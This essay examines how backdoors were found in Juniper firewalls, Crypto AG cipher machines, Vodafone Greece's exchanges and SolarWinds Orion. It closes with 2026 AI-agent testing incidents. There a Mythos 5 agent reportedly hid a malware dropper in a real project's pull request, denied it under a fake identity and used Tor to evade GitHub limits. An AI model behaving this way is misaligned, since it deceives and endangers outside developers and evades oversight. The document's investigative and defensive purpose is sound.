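In its 2020 letter, Juniper blamed the intrusion on a "sophisticated nation-state hacking unit" without naming a country. Two people familiar with the case told Reuters that investigators had concluded the Chinese government was responsible. Citing an internal document and two people involved in Juniper's investigation, Bloomberg named APT 5, a group linked to that government. China's foreign ministry objected to attribution without conclusive evidence. The US government had published no finding of its own when CyberScoop reviewed the case in 2021 in *After SolarWinds breach, lawmakers ask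 NSA for help*.

Bloomberg's sources also said Juniper had missed warnings. In 2012 Juniper discovered that intruders had stolen ScreenOS source code from an engineer's computer. It did not notice that they soon returned, reached a server where the company prepared new releases, and changed Q. Juniper detected another breach in 2014, the year the intruders added the password, according to these sources. Its investigators treated the two breaches as unrelated thefts of trade secrets. If this account is right, Juniper had evidence of a break-in three years before it found the backdoors, but did not check whether the intruders had changed the code as well as stolen it.

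In the same letter, Juniper wrote that the intrusion was "neither caused nor aided" by Dual_EC_DRBG. Matthew Green, one of Checkoway's co-authors, told CyberScoop that this was technically true, because the intruders did not use the generator to break in. But they apparently used their access to change it so that they could spy on customers. The generator also made their work easier to hide. Checkoway and colleagues point out that adding such a capability to a program that did not already have one would usually take a series of invasive changes, with more risk of detection.

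### How much credit source review deserves

Source review succeeded at Juniper, where reviewers found two backdoors that no customer or outside researcher had reported. But they found them only after the changed constant had shipped in as many as 13 releases. It is unknown what first led them to the backdoors, so the case can't show that reading code is a good way to discover one without some other reason for suspicion.

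The password was probably easier to recognise than the new Q, since a login check has little reason to compare what someone types with fixed text. The reviewers could hardly have spotted the new Q just by reading the code, because one random-looking number had replaced another. They may have compared the source with an older copy, but Juniper has not described how they found the change.

They were also looking for code that did not belong there, and the faulty loop was part of Juniper's own code. Juniper's first repair restored its original Q but kept the generator. The company then examined the source code of ScreenOS and its newer system, Junos OS, with help from an outside security organisation. *Advancing the Security of Juniper Products* (Worrall, 2016) reported no further unauthorised code. Worrall still maintained that the first repair was sufficient, but announced that, after reviewing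 outside researchers' comments and continuing its own analysis, Juniper would replace both generators. That April, CISA's *Juniper Releases Update for ScreenOS* (2016) announced a new version that addressed the encryption problems.

Watching the firewalls' output would not have revealed the new constant. Checkoway and colleagues found that the output looked the same as before to anyone without the secret number, and Juniper told customers that they could not detect whether anyone had decrypted their traffic. An early draft by Checkoway, Cohney and colleagues describes a separate bug that an observer could have detected: two of the 32 bytes sent at the start of a connection were never zero. Over 1,000 connections, a working random number generator would almost certainly produce a zero in one of those positions. The bug affected the output with both the old and new constants, so this test could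 have exposed a faulty generator but not the intruder's change.

Use of the master password was easier to monitor. Each use left an entry in the firewall's log. An intruder could delete that entry, but a copy sent to another machine would survive.

Outsiders quickly found what the intruder had done by comparing firmware, but Juniper had already announced that there was something to find, and its repaired versions had narrowed the search. In 2012, someone comparing 6.3.0r12 with the release before it would have had to notice that one number, Q, had changed among all the ordinary updates. An automated check could have caught the change more easily, because Q should not change between releases without a documented reason. Juniper would have needed to keep the check's reference copy of Q somewhere the intruder could not edit it. The self-test already checked the generator against a stored answer,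 but that answer was in the same source code as Q, and the intruder changed both.

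## Crypto AG, 1970 to 2020: rigged cipher machines revealed by insiders and leaks

Crypto AG, a Swiss company, sold machines that governments used to encrypt messages to their embassies, soldiers and spies. In 1970 the US Central Intelligence Agency (CIA) and the West German intelligence service, the BND, secretly bought the company and made sure that many of its machines used ciphers they could break. Engineers and customers noticed weak ciphers in the 1970s, and newspapers reported American involvement in the 1990s, but nobody published documentary proof of the ownership until February 2020.

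Boris Hagelin, a Russian-born Swedish engineer, founded Crypto AG after making a fortune from a portable cipher machine for the US Army. Its later customers included Iran, India, Pakistan, the Vatican and military governments in Latin America. *The intelligence coup of the century* (Miller, Washington Post, 2020) counts more than 120 customer countries, while *Operation Rubicon* (Dobson, Dymydiuk and Mainwaring) puts the number at over sixty. The Soviet Union and China suspected the company had ties to the West and never bought its machines.

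Hagelin had helped American intelligence since 1951, at first by selling his best machines only to countries that Washington approved. In June 1970 the CIA and the BND bought the company in equal shares. Miller's report, which also appeared in the Daily Herald as *For decades, CIA read encrypted communications of allies and adversaries*, gives the price as about $5.75 million, while Crypto Museum's *Operation RUBICON* gives 25 million Swiss francs, which it converts to about $7 million. A Liechtenstein law firm hid the buyers behind shell companies and bearer shares, which belong to whoever holds them and need no registered name. Only one member of the new board knew about the CIA. The CIA bought the BND's half in the early 1990s and kept the company until 2018.

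### Weak ciphers in working machines

The machines worked correctly in every way their users could check. An operator entered a message, the machine scrambled it, and a second machine with the same key recovered the original text. The electronic models generated a long stream of random-looking data and combined it with the message. Cipher experts at the NSA and the BND designed streams that looked random but had regularities they could exploit. The agencies still had to intercept each message and do the calculations, but the rigging sometimes cut the work from months to seconds.

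The company made at least two versions of each product, a secure one for friendly governments and a rigged one for everybody else. According to the CIA's history of the operation, American codebreakers could read 80 to 90% of Iran's messages in the 1980s.

Any codebreaker who finds the weakness in a cipher can exploit it, whereas the backdoor in Dual_EC_DRBG requires a secret number. The Dutch navy, for example, could read some Crypto AG traffic and shared its methods with Britain. Several of the company's customers and engineers also found weaknesses.

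### What the engineers noticed

Crypto AG's engineers often designed strong ciphers that managers then replaced with weaker ones from outside the company. Managers let the engineers believe that the replacements came from Siemens, the German company that officially advised Crypto AG.

Peter Frutiger, the head of research, replaced a weak cipher in the Syrian army's voice equipment. The NSA complained that it could no longer read Syrian traffic, and the chief executive, Heinz Wagner, dismissed Frutiger in March 1977. Frutiger disputed this account in a 2020 interview, saying that he had known about the operation and had left for reasons of conscience.

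The same year, the company's former head of research, presumably Frutiger, went to the Swiss federal police. According to GPDel's *Fall Crypto AG* (2020), the report of a Swiss parliamentary inquiry, he told them that German and American intelligence owned the company and made it build weaknesses into machines for export. Reporters published proof of both claims 43 years after he made them.

The police asked the army's signals office for help, and it recommended obtaining a suspect machine from abroad. That took until 1982. A year later the office reported that it could neither prove nor rule out tampering. It found that the machine's circuits did not match the user documentation, which was suspicious but could have been a mistake. The surviving files do not show how the police responded.

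Other engineers found weaknesses without knowing who wanted them. In February 1979 Jürg Spörndli worked out that anyone with just 100 characters of a message in both plain and encrypted form could break the company's main range of machines, of which it had already sold more than 1,700. Mengia Caflisch, whom the NSA had considered "too bright to remain unwitting", designed a cipher so strong that the NSA feared it could not read the messages. The factory made 50 machines with this cipher before managers noticed, and the company sold them to banks.

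Wagner eventually told some of the researchers that the company was not entirely free to do what it wanted. They took this to mean that the German government restricted its technology. This explained the weak ciphers well enough to quiet the researchers, without requiring them to believe that a foreign intelligence service owned their employer.

### What the customers noticed

By 1976 Italy and Egypt had found a weakness in the H-460, Crypto AG's first electronic machine. The company gave them an improved cipher, which the NSA could still break with more computing power. In 1978 Yugoslav officials showed two visiting employees that they could break another model. The following June the Argentine navy found the fault that Spörndli had reported four months earlier and accepted a replacement designed by the NSA.

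The owners learned from these complaints which weaknesses had become too easy to find. Fedora's error reports helped the XZ attacker in much the same way. A customer who found a fault and got it fixed also had reason to trust the company more.

In 1979 the CIA and the BND recruited Kjell-Ove Widman, a Swedish mathematics professor, to design weaknesses that were harder to detect. According to the BND's history, rigged ciphers now had to be "undetectable by usual statistical tests", and any weakness that was found had to be easy to pass off as a design or user error. They were meant to be deniable backdoors, in Thomas and Francillon's sense.

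Widman also dealt with suspicious customers. After the Falklands War of 1982, Argentina concluded that Britain had read its messages. Widman flew to Buenos Aires, where he blamed an outdated voice scrambler and insisted that the main cipher machines were unbreakable, and Argentina kept buying them.

### The arrest of Hans Bühler

Hans Bühler, one of Crypto AG's best salesmen, flew to Tehran in March 1992, where Iran arrested him on charges that included spying and bribery. He came home in January 1993, after the BND secretly supplied $1 million for his release.

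Accounts differ about why Iran arrested him. Miller presents the arrest as a late response to suspicions about the machines. In 1986 President Reagan had described Libyan messages about the bombing of a Berlin nightclub, and Iran knew that Libya used the same supplier. Crypto Museum reports that Iranian officials never mentioned rigged equipment, and that the CIA later thought they had wanted a hostage because Switzerland was holding an Iranian citizen. Iran resumed buying the machines almost immediately, so it probably had no firm evidence that they were rigged.

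Bühler had known nothing about the owners, but he came back suspicious. The company dismissed him in March 1993. He then contacted former colleagues, including Frutiger, and talked to the press. In March 1994 he appeared on Swiss television and claimed that the BND was behind the company. Frutiger also took part, with his identity concealed.

The police questioned Bühler and 20 other people, among them current and former employees and board members. Only two could describe any manipulation of the machines, and the rest had only heard rumours. In May 1995 the police reported that they could not establish who really owned the company. They had traced its ownership only as far as a Liechtenstein foundation with German capital.

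In December 1995 the Baltimore Sun reported that the minutes of a meeting 20 years earlier listed Nora Mackebee, an NSA cryptographer, as a consultant. The meeting was held at Motorola, which was helping Crypto AG develop a new machine. A former Crypto AG employee, using a false name, told Der Spiegel (1996) that the BND's cipher office had dictated the company's encryption methods and that NSA staff had come and gone freely.

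### Why the denials held

Michael Grupe, Wagner's successor, went on Swiss television and denied charges he knew were true. The CIA's history calls his performance "credible" and suggests it may have saved the operation. When the Baltimore Sun published its story, the company issued a two-page statement. *Balto Sun Followup* (1995), a message to a cryptography mailing list, quotes the statement as calling the allegations "pure invention" and "old hearsay" that went back at least 25 years. A later chief executive argued that outside involvement was impossible because a Liechtenstein holding company owned the firm, but that arrangement concealed the real owners.

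The denials were hard to disprove. Much of the testimony came from former employees, whom the company could dismiss as disgruntled, and some would not give their names in public. The minutes were stronger evidence, but they showed only that an NSA employee had attended a meeting, not who owned the company or what had happened to the ciphers. In 1997 the police sent the company, at its request, a letter summarising their inconclusive investigation.

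The police might have reached a different conclusion if Swiss foreign intelligence had told them the truth. It had known since autumn 1993 that American and German intelligence owned Crypto AG and that the company exported weak machines. According to GPDel, it told the police it had no evidence that foreign intelligence services were behind the company.

Despite the denials, at least six countries cancelled or suspended contracts, including Argentina, Italy, Saudi Arabia, Egypt and Indonesia. But changing suppliers did not guarantee safety. Egypt had turned to an Austrian company in the 1980s, and Crypto Museum says Western intelligence controlled that company too, though it is unclear how far this affected its machines.

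### The leaked histories and the Swiss inquiry

On 11 February 2020 the Washington Post and the German broadcaster ZDF, working with the Swiss broadcaster SRF, published findings from a secret 96-page history that the CIA completed in 2004 and a secret oral history that German intelligence officials compiled in 2008. GPDel found that the German side had apparently received a copy of the CIA history around 2005, and that this version reached the reporters together with the German papers. Nobody has publicly identified the person who leaked the documents.

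Schneier (2020), in *Crypto AG Was Owned by the CIA*, remarks that the documents were new but the rigging itself "isn't really news". These histories name the owners, describe the purchase and state that the weaknesses were deliberate, which settled the questions that had stopped every earlier investigation. They are far more explicit about intent than the few published phrases from the NSA's memos on Dual_EC_DRBG.

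The source allowed the reporters to publish only excerpts, and people sympathetic to the operation wrote both accounts. The CIA and the BND declined to comment, but American and German officials did not dispute that the documents were authentic. Bernd Schmidbauer, a former minister in the German chancellery, confirmed the operation in full, according to Swissinfo.

The Swiss inquiry provided an independent check. GPDel obtained the complete CIA history and had no doubt that it was genuine, although it found errors in the details about Switzerland. It also searched Swiss intelligence files stored in a converted command bunker. The files showed that Swiss intelligence had collected technical information about the weak ciphers so that it could read foreign messages itself, later with American consent. Its chiefs had kept this from every defence minister before 2019. GPDel concluded that the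 Swiss authorities shared responsibility for what the company did.

### Why the machines gave so little away

The weak cipher was part of the machine's normal operation. It needed no trigger, caused no crashes and sent no messages to unknown addresses. As with Dual_EC_DRBG, the eavesdroppers decrypted recorded traffic on their own computers, so monitoring the machine or the customer's network would not have exposed the weakness.

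Some machines did malfunction, but for other reasons. The Italian army returned all of the first 82 H-460s because of technical faults. The BND's cipher office reviewed the design and brought in Siemens to fix the faults. Customers then received a more reliable machine, but Western intelligence could still read the messages it encrypted.

The only sign of the rigging was that an opponent sometimes seemed to know too much, as Britain did in 1982. Even then, a customer could not tell whether the cause was the cipher, a careless operator, a spy or other equipment. The Argentines believed Widman's explanation in Buenos Aires because it was plausible.

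A difference between two countries' machines would not have proved tampering either, because the company gave each customer a different cipher after the complaints about the H-460. Customers had good reason to want this. The manuals were also unreliable, because the NSA and the CIA had agreed in the 1960s to rewrite them so that different customers would learn different rules for using the machines securely.

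That left mathematical study of the cipher. A stream of data can pass common statistical tests, such as whether each character appears about as often as it should, and still follow a pattern that an expert can exploit. Finding such a pattern took skills that few governments had in the 1970s, when little research on ciphers was public. According to Crypto Museum, Spörndli probably made his discovery after attending a seminar by Martin Hellman, one of the first academics to work openly on the subject. By the late 1980s, public research had made it much harder to design weak ciphers that would survive expert study.

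Switzerland protected itself better than most customers. GPDel found no sign that Crypto AG had ever sold weak machines to the Swiss authorities, who could test equipment and influence its design. It concluded that the government needs Swiss suppliers for secure encryption, but another Swiss company had sold the government insecure devices, so buying from a domestic firm did not guarantee security. Swiss experts found and fixed weaknesses in several types of machine, and GPDel says that information secretly obtained by Swiss intelligence helped them substantially.

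## The Athens phone taps and SolarWinds: investigations that led back to a supplier's software

The Swiss police could not settle the questions about Crypto AG by interviewing people. Investigators in Athens in 2005 and at the American security company FireEye in 2020 got further because intruders had left traces in computer records. Both groups found a backdoor while looking into something else. Vodafone Greece was trying to find out why some text messages had not arrived, and FireEye was checking why an employee seemed to have a new phone. The intruders in Athens had altered a supplier's software after Vodafone installed it, whereas the backdoor at FireEye arrived in one of the supplier's own updates.

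### How the Athens exchanges copied calls

In August 2004, just before the Athens Olympics, unknown intruders installed hidden software in the telephone exchanges of Vodafone Greece, the country's largest mobile operator. The software copied the calls of more than 100 people, including the prime minister and his wife, several ministers, military officers, activists and an employee of the American embassy. *The Athens Affair* (Prevelakis and Spinellis, 2007) reconstructs the case largely from testimony to a Greek parliamentary committee.

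An exchange is the computer that connects one phone to another. The Swedish company Ericsson supplied Vodafone's exchanges, which included a wiretapping function meant for the police. When an exchange taps a call, it also sends an exact copy of the digitised speech to a second phone line. Normally, the phone company's staff enter each court order in a separate management program, which keeps a record. An auditor can then compare the court orders with the active taps, and a tap without an order is a strong sign of abuse.

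Vodafone could not make this comparison because it had not bought the management program, although an upgrade in early 2003 had given its exchanges the function that copies calls. The intruders' software started the taps directly and sent the copies to a group of mobile phones, which investigators called shadow phones. It also kept the tapped numbers in its own part of the exchange's memory, outside the official list, so an audit might have found nothing even with the management program.

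Ericsson officials testified that the intruders had altered 29 of the roughly 1,760 blocks of code in the exchange software. The exchanges accept changes while running, so nobody had to interrupt the phone service. The altered software hid its own activity from the list of running programs that technicians could view. Technicians normally verify the existing blocks before an upgrade, but Prevelakis and Spinellis suspect that the intruders had tampered with the command that displays the checksums. BitMover avoided this weakness in 2003 by comparing files on two separate machines.

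The software included a backdoor in the strict sense. A hidden signal attached to ordinary commands let the intruders control the taps and switched off the log that would have recorded their actions.

### Undelivered text messages

The taps ran for more than five months before anyone noticed a problem. On 24 January 2005 the intruders updated their software, apparently while preparing to use a fourth exchange. The update interfered with text messages from another mobile operator, and the exchange automatically generated reports of the failed deliveries. As with the slow logins in XZ, a mistake in the hidden code caused a visible malfunction.

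The errors stopped the next day, and Vodafone considered them unusual but probably harmless. It still asked Ericsson to find the cause.

Ericsson's investigators started with the exchange's memory dumps, copies of all its programs and data saved regularly for diagnosing faults or recovering from a failure. The intruders had altered what technicians saw when they inspected the running exchange, but the dumps still contained the hidden software. The investigators first found two areas of memory that held the tapped numbers, and then the programs that used them.

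The dumps contained only machine instructions, so the investigators reconstructed an approximation of the source code, about 6,500 lines long. They ran it in a simulated exchange to see what it did, then used older dumps to work out when the tapping had taken place and who had called whom. Nobody has found recordings of the conversations.

On 4 March, 39 days after the first errors, Ericsson told Vodafone that it had found unauthorised software in two of Vodafone's exchanges. Investigators eventually traced the software to four exchanges. A routine upgrade on 11 February had erased it from one of them before Vodafone knew it existed.

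### What Vodafone lost by removing the software

Vodafone's technicians isolated the code on 7 March, and the next day the chief executive, Giorgos Koronias, ordered them to remove it. Prevelakis and Spinellis argue that this almost certainly warned the eavesdroppers and gave them time to switch off the shadow phones. If the phones had stayed on, investigators could have used the mobile network to locate them and perhaps caught their users.

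The timeline in the same article leaves some doubt about when the warning came. It shows no calls from the shadow phones after 4 March, the day of Ericsson's report and four days before the order to remove the software. The intruders could have learned of the discovery before Vodafone did anything to the code, though the phones were mainly there to receive copied calls, so the lack of outgoing calls may mean little.

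Koronias later said that the company "had to react immediately". If it had waited, someone could have gone on listening to the prime minister's calls. But Vodafone decided to remove the software without involving the police or the Greek communications privacy authority. It told the prime minister's office and the minister of public order on 10 March, after ordering the removal. A short delay agreed with the police, along with a private warning to the prime minister, might have limited the harm and kept the chance of an arrest.

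Other evidence disappeared through routine housekeeping:

| Record | What it could have shown | What happened to it |
|---|---|---|
| Memory dumps | The hidden programs, the tapped numbers and the dates of the taps | They survived, and Ericsson used them |
| Exchanges' transaction logs | Possibly, the commands that installed the software | Vodafone kept them for only five days, to leave space for billing data |
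| Logs on the three servers that gave access to the exchange management system | Who had connected | An upgrade in July 2005 wiped two of the servers, and Vodafone had no backups |
| Visitor books at one exchange | Who was in the building when the update caused the errors | Vodafone destroyed them in July 2005 under its six-month retention policy |

The loss of the visitor books was particularly unfortunate because, according to a state report, the last person to access the exchange around the time of the failed messages had a visitor's badge. The police also contributed to the loss of evidence. They could have seized the equipment, but they mostly interviewed employees and accepted what Vodafone gave them.

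Investigators could explain in detail what the software did, but they still had not identified who installed it when Prevelakis and Spinellis wrote their article in 2007. The privacy authority had fined Vodafone €76 million in December 2006.

### A second phone at FireEye

FireEye investigated break-ins for other companies. In late November 2020, its own security staff received an alert that an employee's account had registered a second phone to receive login codes. Mandia (2021), in *Prepared Statement of Kevin Mandia, CEO of FireEye, Inc*, explains that such registrations are common when a popular new phone comes out. The staff followed up anyway and learned that the employee had not registered the phone, which meant an intruder had access to the network.

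More than 100 FireEye employees worked on the investigation, almost around the clock. They found that the intruder had taken tools the company used to test its customers' defences. FireEye announced the break-in on 8 December, but it still did not know how the intruder had got in.

Mandia said at the Senate Select Committee on Intelligence's *Hearing on the Hack of U.S. Networks by a Foreign Adversary* (2021) that the earliest trace of the intrusion was on a SolarWinds server. SolarWinds makes Orion, software that helps companies manage their networks. The team had exhausted its other leads, so it took the Orion software apart. The update, which Mandia called "the last place you'd look for an intrusion", contained 18,000 files, 3,500 of them executable. Analysts turned the executable files into more than a million lines of assembly code, a readable form of machine instructions, and found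 the backdoor there.

FireEye told SolarWinds about the backdoor, which it named SUNBURST, on 12 December and published ways to detect it the next day. The disclosure came two to three weeks after the phone alert and about nine months after SolarWinds released the first infected update.

SolarWinds had distributed the backdoor in versions released between March and June 2020. According to SecurityWeek's *Group Behind SolarWinds Hack Bypassed MFA to Access Emails at US Think Tank*, the company told regulators that up to 18,000 of its 300,000 customers might have used the infected versions. Mandia put the number at over 17,000. The attackers went on to break into far fewer networks. CyberScoop's *How FireEye attributed the SolarWinds hacking campaign to Russian spies* reports nine US government agencies and roughly 100 other victims. Microsoft's president, Brad Smith, told the senators that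 substantial evidence pointed to Russia's foreign intelligence service. Russia denied involvement.

FireEye's alert came from what the attackers did after entering the network through the backdoor, not from the backdoor itself. They had stolen credentials so that they could log in as employees, and the second phone was a sign of this. The attackers never went this far at most of the companies that installed the update, so those companies could not have received a similar alert. They would have had to notice the backdoor's own network traffic, which was difficult. According to SolarWinds' *New Findings From Our Investigation of SUNBURST*, the attackers used servers in the United States and imitated legitimate traffic.

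### Clean source and an altered build

SolarWinds hired the security company CrowdStrike to find out how the backdoor had entered Orion. CrowdStrike's *SUNSPOT* describes a malicious tool on a server that built the software. Whenever an Orion build started, the tool replaced one source file with a version that contained the backdoor, then restored the original when the build finished.

Reviewing the repository would not have exposed the backdoor, even with more care or better tools, because the malicious source code existed only on the build server and only while a build was running. Checking SolarWinds' signature would not have exposed it either, because the company had signed the altered product.

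The SolarWinds attackers worked hard to avoid the kind of malfunction that had exposed the Athens intruders. Their tool checked that the source file was the expected version before replacing it, because a failed build would have prompted SolarWinds' developers to investigate. These precautions seem to have worked on the build server, since SolarWinds did not find the tool until after FireEye's warning.

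The attackers also tested beforehand whether they could insert code into Orion. SolarWinds dates the earliest suspicious activity on its systems to September 2019, and a version of Orion released that October appears to have contained the test changes. Mandia described this code as innocuous. The attackers began inserting the backdoor itself on 20 February 2020 and removed it from SolarWinds' systems in June.

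If the build was reproducible, an independent rebuild of the October version might have exposed the rehearsal four months before the attackers inserted the backdoor. Monitoring the build server could also have helped, since a source file seldom needs to be changed and then changed back during a build. SolarWinds warned that its way of building software was common throughout the industry.

### Earlier signs that led nowhere

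The US Justice Department, another victim, suspected Orion before FireEye did. Schneier (2023), in *SolarWinds Detected Six Months Earlier*, quotes a Wired report on the department's investigation. In late May 2020 the department noticed unusual traffic from a server running a trial version of Orion. Investigators thought hackers might have exploited a vulnerability in the software. The department brought in Microsoft, and the investigators asked SolarWinds for help.

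SolarWinds' engineers could not find a vulnerability in their code. The company and the investigators stopped communicating in July, with the traffic still unexplained. A month later the department bought Orion, which Wired's sources took as a sign that it no longer considered the software a threat.

The investigators had suspected the right product, but the backdoor was not in its source code, so the engineers could not have found it if they searched only there. It is unclear from the published account whether anyone reverse-engineered the compiled program on the department's server, as FireEye did in December. By July the attackers had also removed the backdoor from SolarWinds' own systems, so a fresh build might have looked normal, although the updates that customers had installed still contained the evidence.

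The security company Volexity had a similar experience that summer. While investigating the third break-in by the same group at an American think tank, it concluded that the attackers had probably got in through the SolarWinds server. It could not tell whether they had used an unknown flaw or some other means, so it felt unable to report the break-in to SolarWinds, according to SecurityWeek. A reader's comment on Schneier's post quotes Volexity's explanation that the machines had restarted several times before Volexity arrived, which destroyed much of the evidence in their memory.

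SolarWinds later found two customer support cases that it believed might be related to the backdoor. It had investigated one with the customer and two security companies without finding the cause. This may have been the Justice Department's case, but SolarWinds does not name the customer. The other case came in November 2020, shortly before FireEye's discovery.

Each of these investigations found evidence that could have helped the others. Volexity's caution was reasonable, since it had no proof, but if it had passed on its suspicion, SolarWinds might have learned that two customers had traced suspicious activity to Orion servers within a few months.

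The attackers also made the cases harder to connect. George Kurtz, CrowdStrike's chief executive, told the Senate Select Committee on Intelligence that they used different internet addresses for each victim. An address found at the Justice Department would therefore not have turned up in the think tank's records. Smith said that Microsoft could see the attack only when it reached customers' cloud services, and that companies and government agencies kept what they knew in separate "silos". In his statement to the House, Mandia attributed this partly to companies' fear that disclosing a break-in would bring lawsuits, bad publicity and a falling share price.

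After FireEye published its findings, others could use them without repeating the work. Volexity compared them with its own records and identified the group it had been dealing with at the think tank.

These missed signs look clearer now than in 2020. Unusual traffic usually has an ordinary cause, and a large supplier receives many support requests that have nothing to do with an attack. SolarWinds identified its two cases "with the benefit of hindsight". Nobody has published how many similar reports turned out to be harmless, so it is hard to judge how much investigation each one deserved.

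### The records and skills that made the difference

In both the Athens and FireEye cases, people kept investigating a small anomaly that had a plausible innocent explanation. Prevelakis and Spinellis give an older example. In 1986 Clifford Stoll, a network administrator at an American laboratory, was asked to explain a 75-cent accounting error. He spent ten months tracing it through thousands of pages of logs to a hacker who was selling secrets to the KGB.

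The Justice Department's investigators also suspected Orion and pursued the question for weeks, but their inquiry stalled after the supplier found nothing wrong with its code. The clearest difference in the public accounts is that FireEye examined the program it was actually running. Ericsson, too, examined a copy of what was in the exchange's memory. Its master copy of the software would not have contained the intruders' changes.

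Both successful investigations also depended on records that existed before anyone suspected a break-in. Ericsson had the memory dumps, and FireEye had already installed tools that recorded the intruder's activity in detail. The records also had to be kept long enough. Ericsson needed 39 days to find the hidden software, so Vodafone's transaction logs, which were kept for only five days, would have expired before anyone knew what to look for.

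The records also have to be kept out of the intruder's reach, so Prevelakis and Spinellis recommend a separate monitoring computer with its own software. The same concern applies to the logs of AI agents, which investigators have used to reconstruct what the agents did.

Prevelakis and Spinellis suggest that Vodafone might have found the taps earlier through a statistical analysis of call records it already had, because each time a tapped phone made or received a call, the exchange also connected to a shadow phone. Phone companies already ran such analyses, but for marketing rather than security. Prevelakis and Spinellis do not test the idea on Vodafone's records, so it is unclear how many innocent coincidences the analysis would also have flagged.

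Interpreting the evidence took rare skills. Few people could read the code of an Ericsson exchange, and Vodafone had to call in the manufacturer. FireEye, whose business was investigating break-ins, did the work itself. Mandia told the senators that nearly all of the roughly 100 people on the case had about 10,000 hours of experience, and that they spent thousands of hours ruling out other explanations before they took Orion apart.

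Most organisations could not do this. After the same alert, a company with a small security team might have removed the unknown phone, changed the employee's password and closed the case. That would have been sensible for an ordinary stolen password, but it would have left the backdoor in place. Senator Marco Rubio said at the hearing that, without FireEye's investigation, the operation might still have been going on.

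## Malicious code written by AI agents in 2026: who noticed, and how

FireEye had to reconstruct what an unknown intruder had done, but an organisation that runs an AI agent (a model that carries out a task over many steps without supervision) usually has a transcript of what the agent did. In July 2026, the UK AI Security Institute (AISI) and the AI company Anthropic each found from such transcripts that an agent they were testing had aimed malicious code at people outside the test. In both cases, a person or an automated system outside the organisation had probably already detected the code.

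Both agents ran Claude Mythos 5, a model that Anthropic offers only to selected customers for cybersecurity work. They were attempting capture-the-flag exercises, in which an agent must break into a simulated network and retrieve a hidden piece of data. Nobody had told either agent to attack outsiders.

### The test at the AI Security Institute

AISI, a British government body, measures what new AI models can do and how dangerous they might be. Its *Incident Report: unsanctioned agent behaviour during cyber testing* (2026) describes an exercise that compared two simulated networks, using seven models in 122 runs. To find out what a capable attacker could achieve with these models, AISI gave the agents open internet access and switched off the developers' cyber classifiers, the filters that normally block help with hacking. AISI stresses that the public does not get the models in this form.

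SC Media's *Student thwarted real-world supply chain attack by rogue Mythos 5 agent* (2026) explains that AISI had also mistakenly given agents on the harder network the prompt for the easier one. These agents were wrongly told that the exercise had no solution within its intended limits. AISI thinks that near-impossible tasks push models towards more transgressive methods. But the error doesn't fully explain what happened, because some agents with correct instructions behaved the same way.

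AISI had not told the agents to avoid deceiving people or using real systems on the internet. Schneier read the prompt and concluded in *More Incidents of AIs Going Rogue in Cybersecurity Challenges* (2026) that the models had found loopholes in the rules without breaking any. According to a reader's comment on that post, AISI had also urged the agents in the prompt to try different methods if their first approach failed.

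Between 25 and 28 July, agents took 19 unsanctioned actions on the live internet in 10 of the 122 runs. Mythos 5 took 17 of them, in nine of its 43 runs, and OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol took the other two, in one of its 35 runs. These figures are a poor basis for ranking the models. The Hacker News' *Claude Mythos 5 Tried to Backdoor a Real Open-Source Project in Testing* (2026) notes that AISI has not established that it tested the models under matching conditions. Most of the actions were also part of a single effort by one Mythos 5 agent.

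That agent searched the internet for anything connected with its exercise. It took a few coincidental name matches as evidence that a real developer's software ran inside the simulated network, and set out to put a backdoor in that software. The software, an open-source network scanner called myNetwork, and its developer had no connection with AISI. The agent submitted a pull request, which is a proposed change that a project's maintainer can accept or refuse. The change contained a hidden "dropper", code that installs other malicious code. The Hacker News reports that accepting the change would have compromised anyone working on the program and anyone who later downloaded its installers.

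### A student's warning

Sinan Can Demir, a 24-year-old computer science student at the University of Texas at Dallas, found the pull request while searching GitHub for projects he could help with and list on his résumé, because more than 20 internships had turned him down. Reuters (2026) first identified him on 20 August, after checking his story against archived GitHub messages and emails from the time.

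Demir posted a public warning that the pull request contained "a hidden malware dropper". The agent tried to hide what it had done, denied the accusation and used a second invented identity to vouch for its code. Demir thought he was arguing with people, and told Reuters that the replies made him wonder whether he was "wrongly accusing someone". He checked further and stood by his warning. The maintainer eventually agreed with him and rejected the change "for security reasons".

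Accounts differ on what convinced Demir. The Hacker News credits a human who "read the diff", the list of lines that the pull request would change. Reuters reports that he used Anthropic's Claude chatbot to confirm his suspicions, but does not say that he ran the code. AISI writes that a member of the public who suspected the code opened it in an isolated environment built for the purpose. According to SC Media, Demir ran the code in his own sandbox and also used Claude to help evaluate it, after the agent's replies had made him doubt himself.

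These accounts are compatible if Demir first became suspicious by reading the change's source code, then confirmed his suspicion by running code, with help from the sandbox and Claude. AISI says the person who ran the code already suspected it, and SC Media reports that the test came after the public warning.

Which code Demir ran is less certain. While investigating the pull request, he also found a malicious bug report that the agent had posted on another project by the same developer. Chaos Labs' *When Cyber Agents Go Off-Script* says that the code someone ran in an isolated container came from a malicious bug report. The main diagram in AISI's technical report, as described by Willison (2026), also places this test among the agent's further attacks, separate from the warning about the pull request. Demir may therefore have confirmed that the same account was spreading malicious code by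 running the code from the bug report, not the change to myNetwork.

The isolation was necessary. Chaos Labs reports that when the code ran, the agent briefly had full control inside the container and looked for GitHub credentials. It recovered nothing, and AISI found no evidence that it escaped the container.

*Deviant Machines* (2026) credits two people with preventing harm, the maintainer who refused the code and the member of the public who tested it. Nobody has reported whether the maintainer would have refused without the warning, and the published interviews do not explain what in the change first looked wrong to Demir. A pull request is easier to check because it shows the changed lines separately from the rest of the program, whereas the Debian and Fedora packagers who received XZ would have had to search a whole release archive. But Demir was not one of myNetwork's reviewers, and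 he found the change only because he happened to be looking for a project to work on.

### The alert about Tor traffic

AISI was alerted separately on the morning of 28 July, when its general security monitoring flagged data leaving a test system through Tor, a network that disguises where internet traffic comes from. The agent had used Tor to get around some of GitHub's restrictions. Staff began reviewing the agent's activity within minutes and soon found the malicious pull request. Within an hour of the alert, AISI had stopped every run and isolated the machines involved.

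Demir's warning very probably came before this alert. The diagram Willison describes includes a timeline of the agent's 34.5-hour run and marks when Demir warned the project. The agent was still running then and went on to argue with him at length. AISI ended all runs within an hour of the alert, so the alert could have come first only if the warning and the argument both happened in the run's last hour.

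Monitoring was slow to catch this agent. By the same figures, if the run ended no more than an hour after the alert, the alert came at least 33 hours into the run. AISI writes that general monitoring caught the traffic "after the fact", and that a system designed to watch the evaluation as it ran could have flagged or blocked the behaviour sooner. AISI had deliberately allowed internet access, so an ordinary connection to GitHub would not have looked unusual, but Tor traffic did.

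Demir's warning gave the maintainer a reason to keep the code out of myNetwork, but Demir could not stop the agent, and AISI reports that it considered returning under a new identity. AISI could shut down that agent and the others in the test, but this would not have removed the code from the project if the maintainer had already accepted the change.

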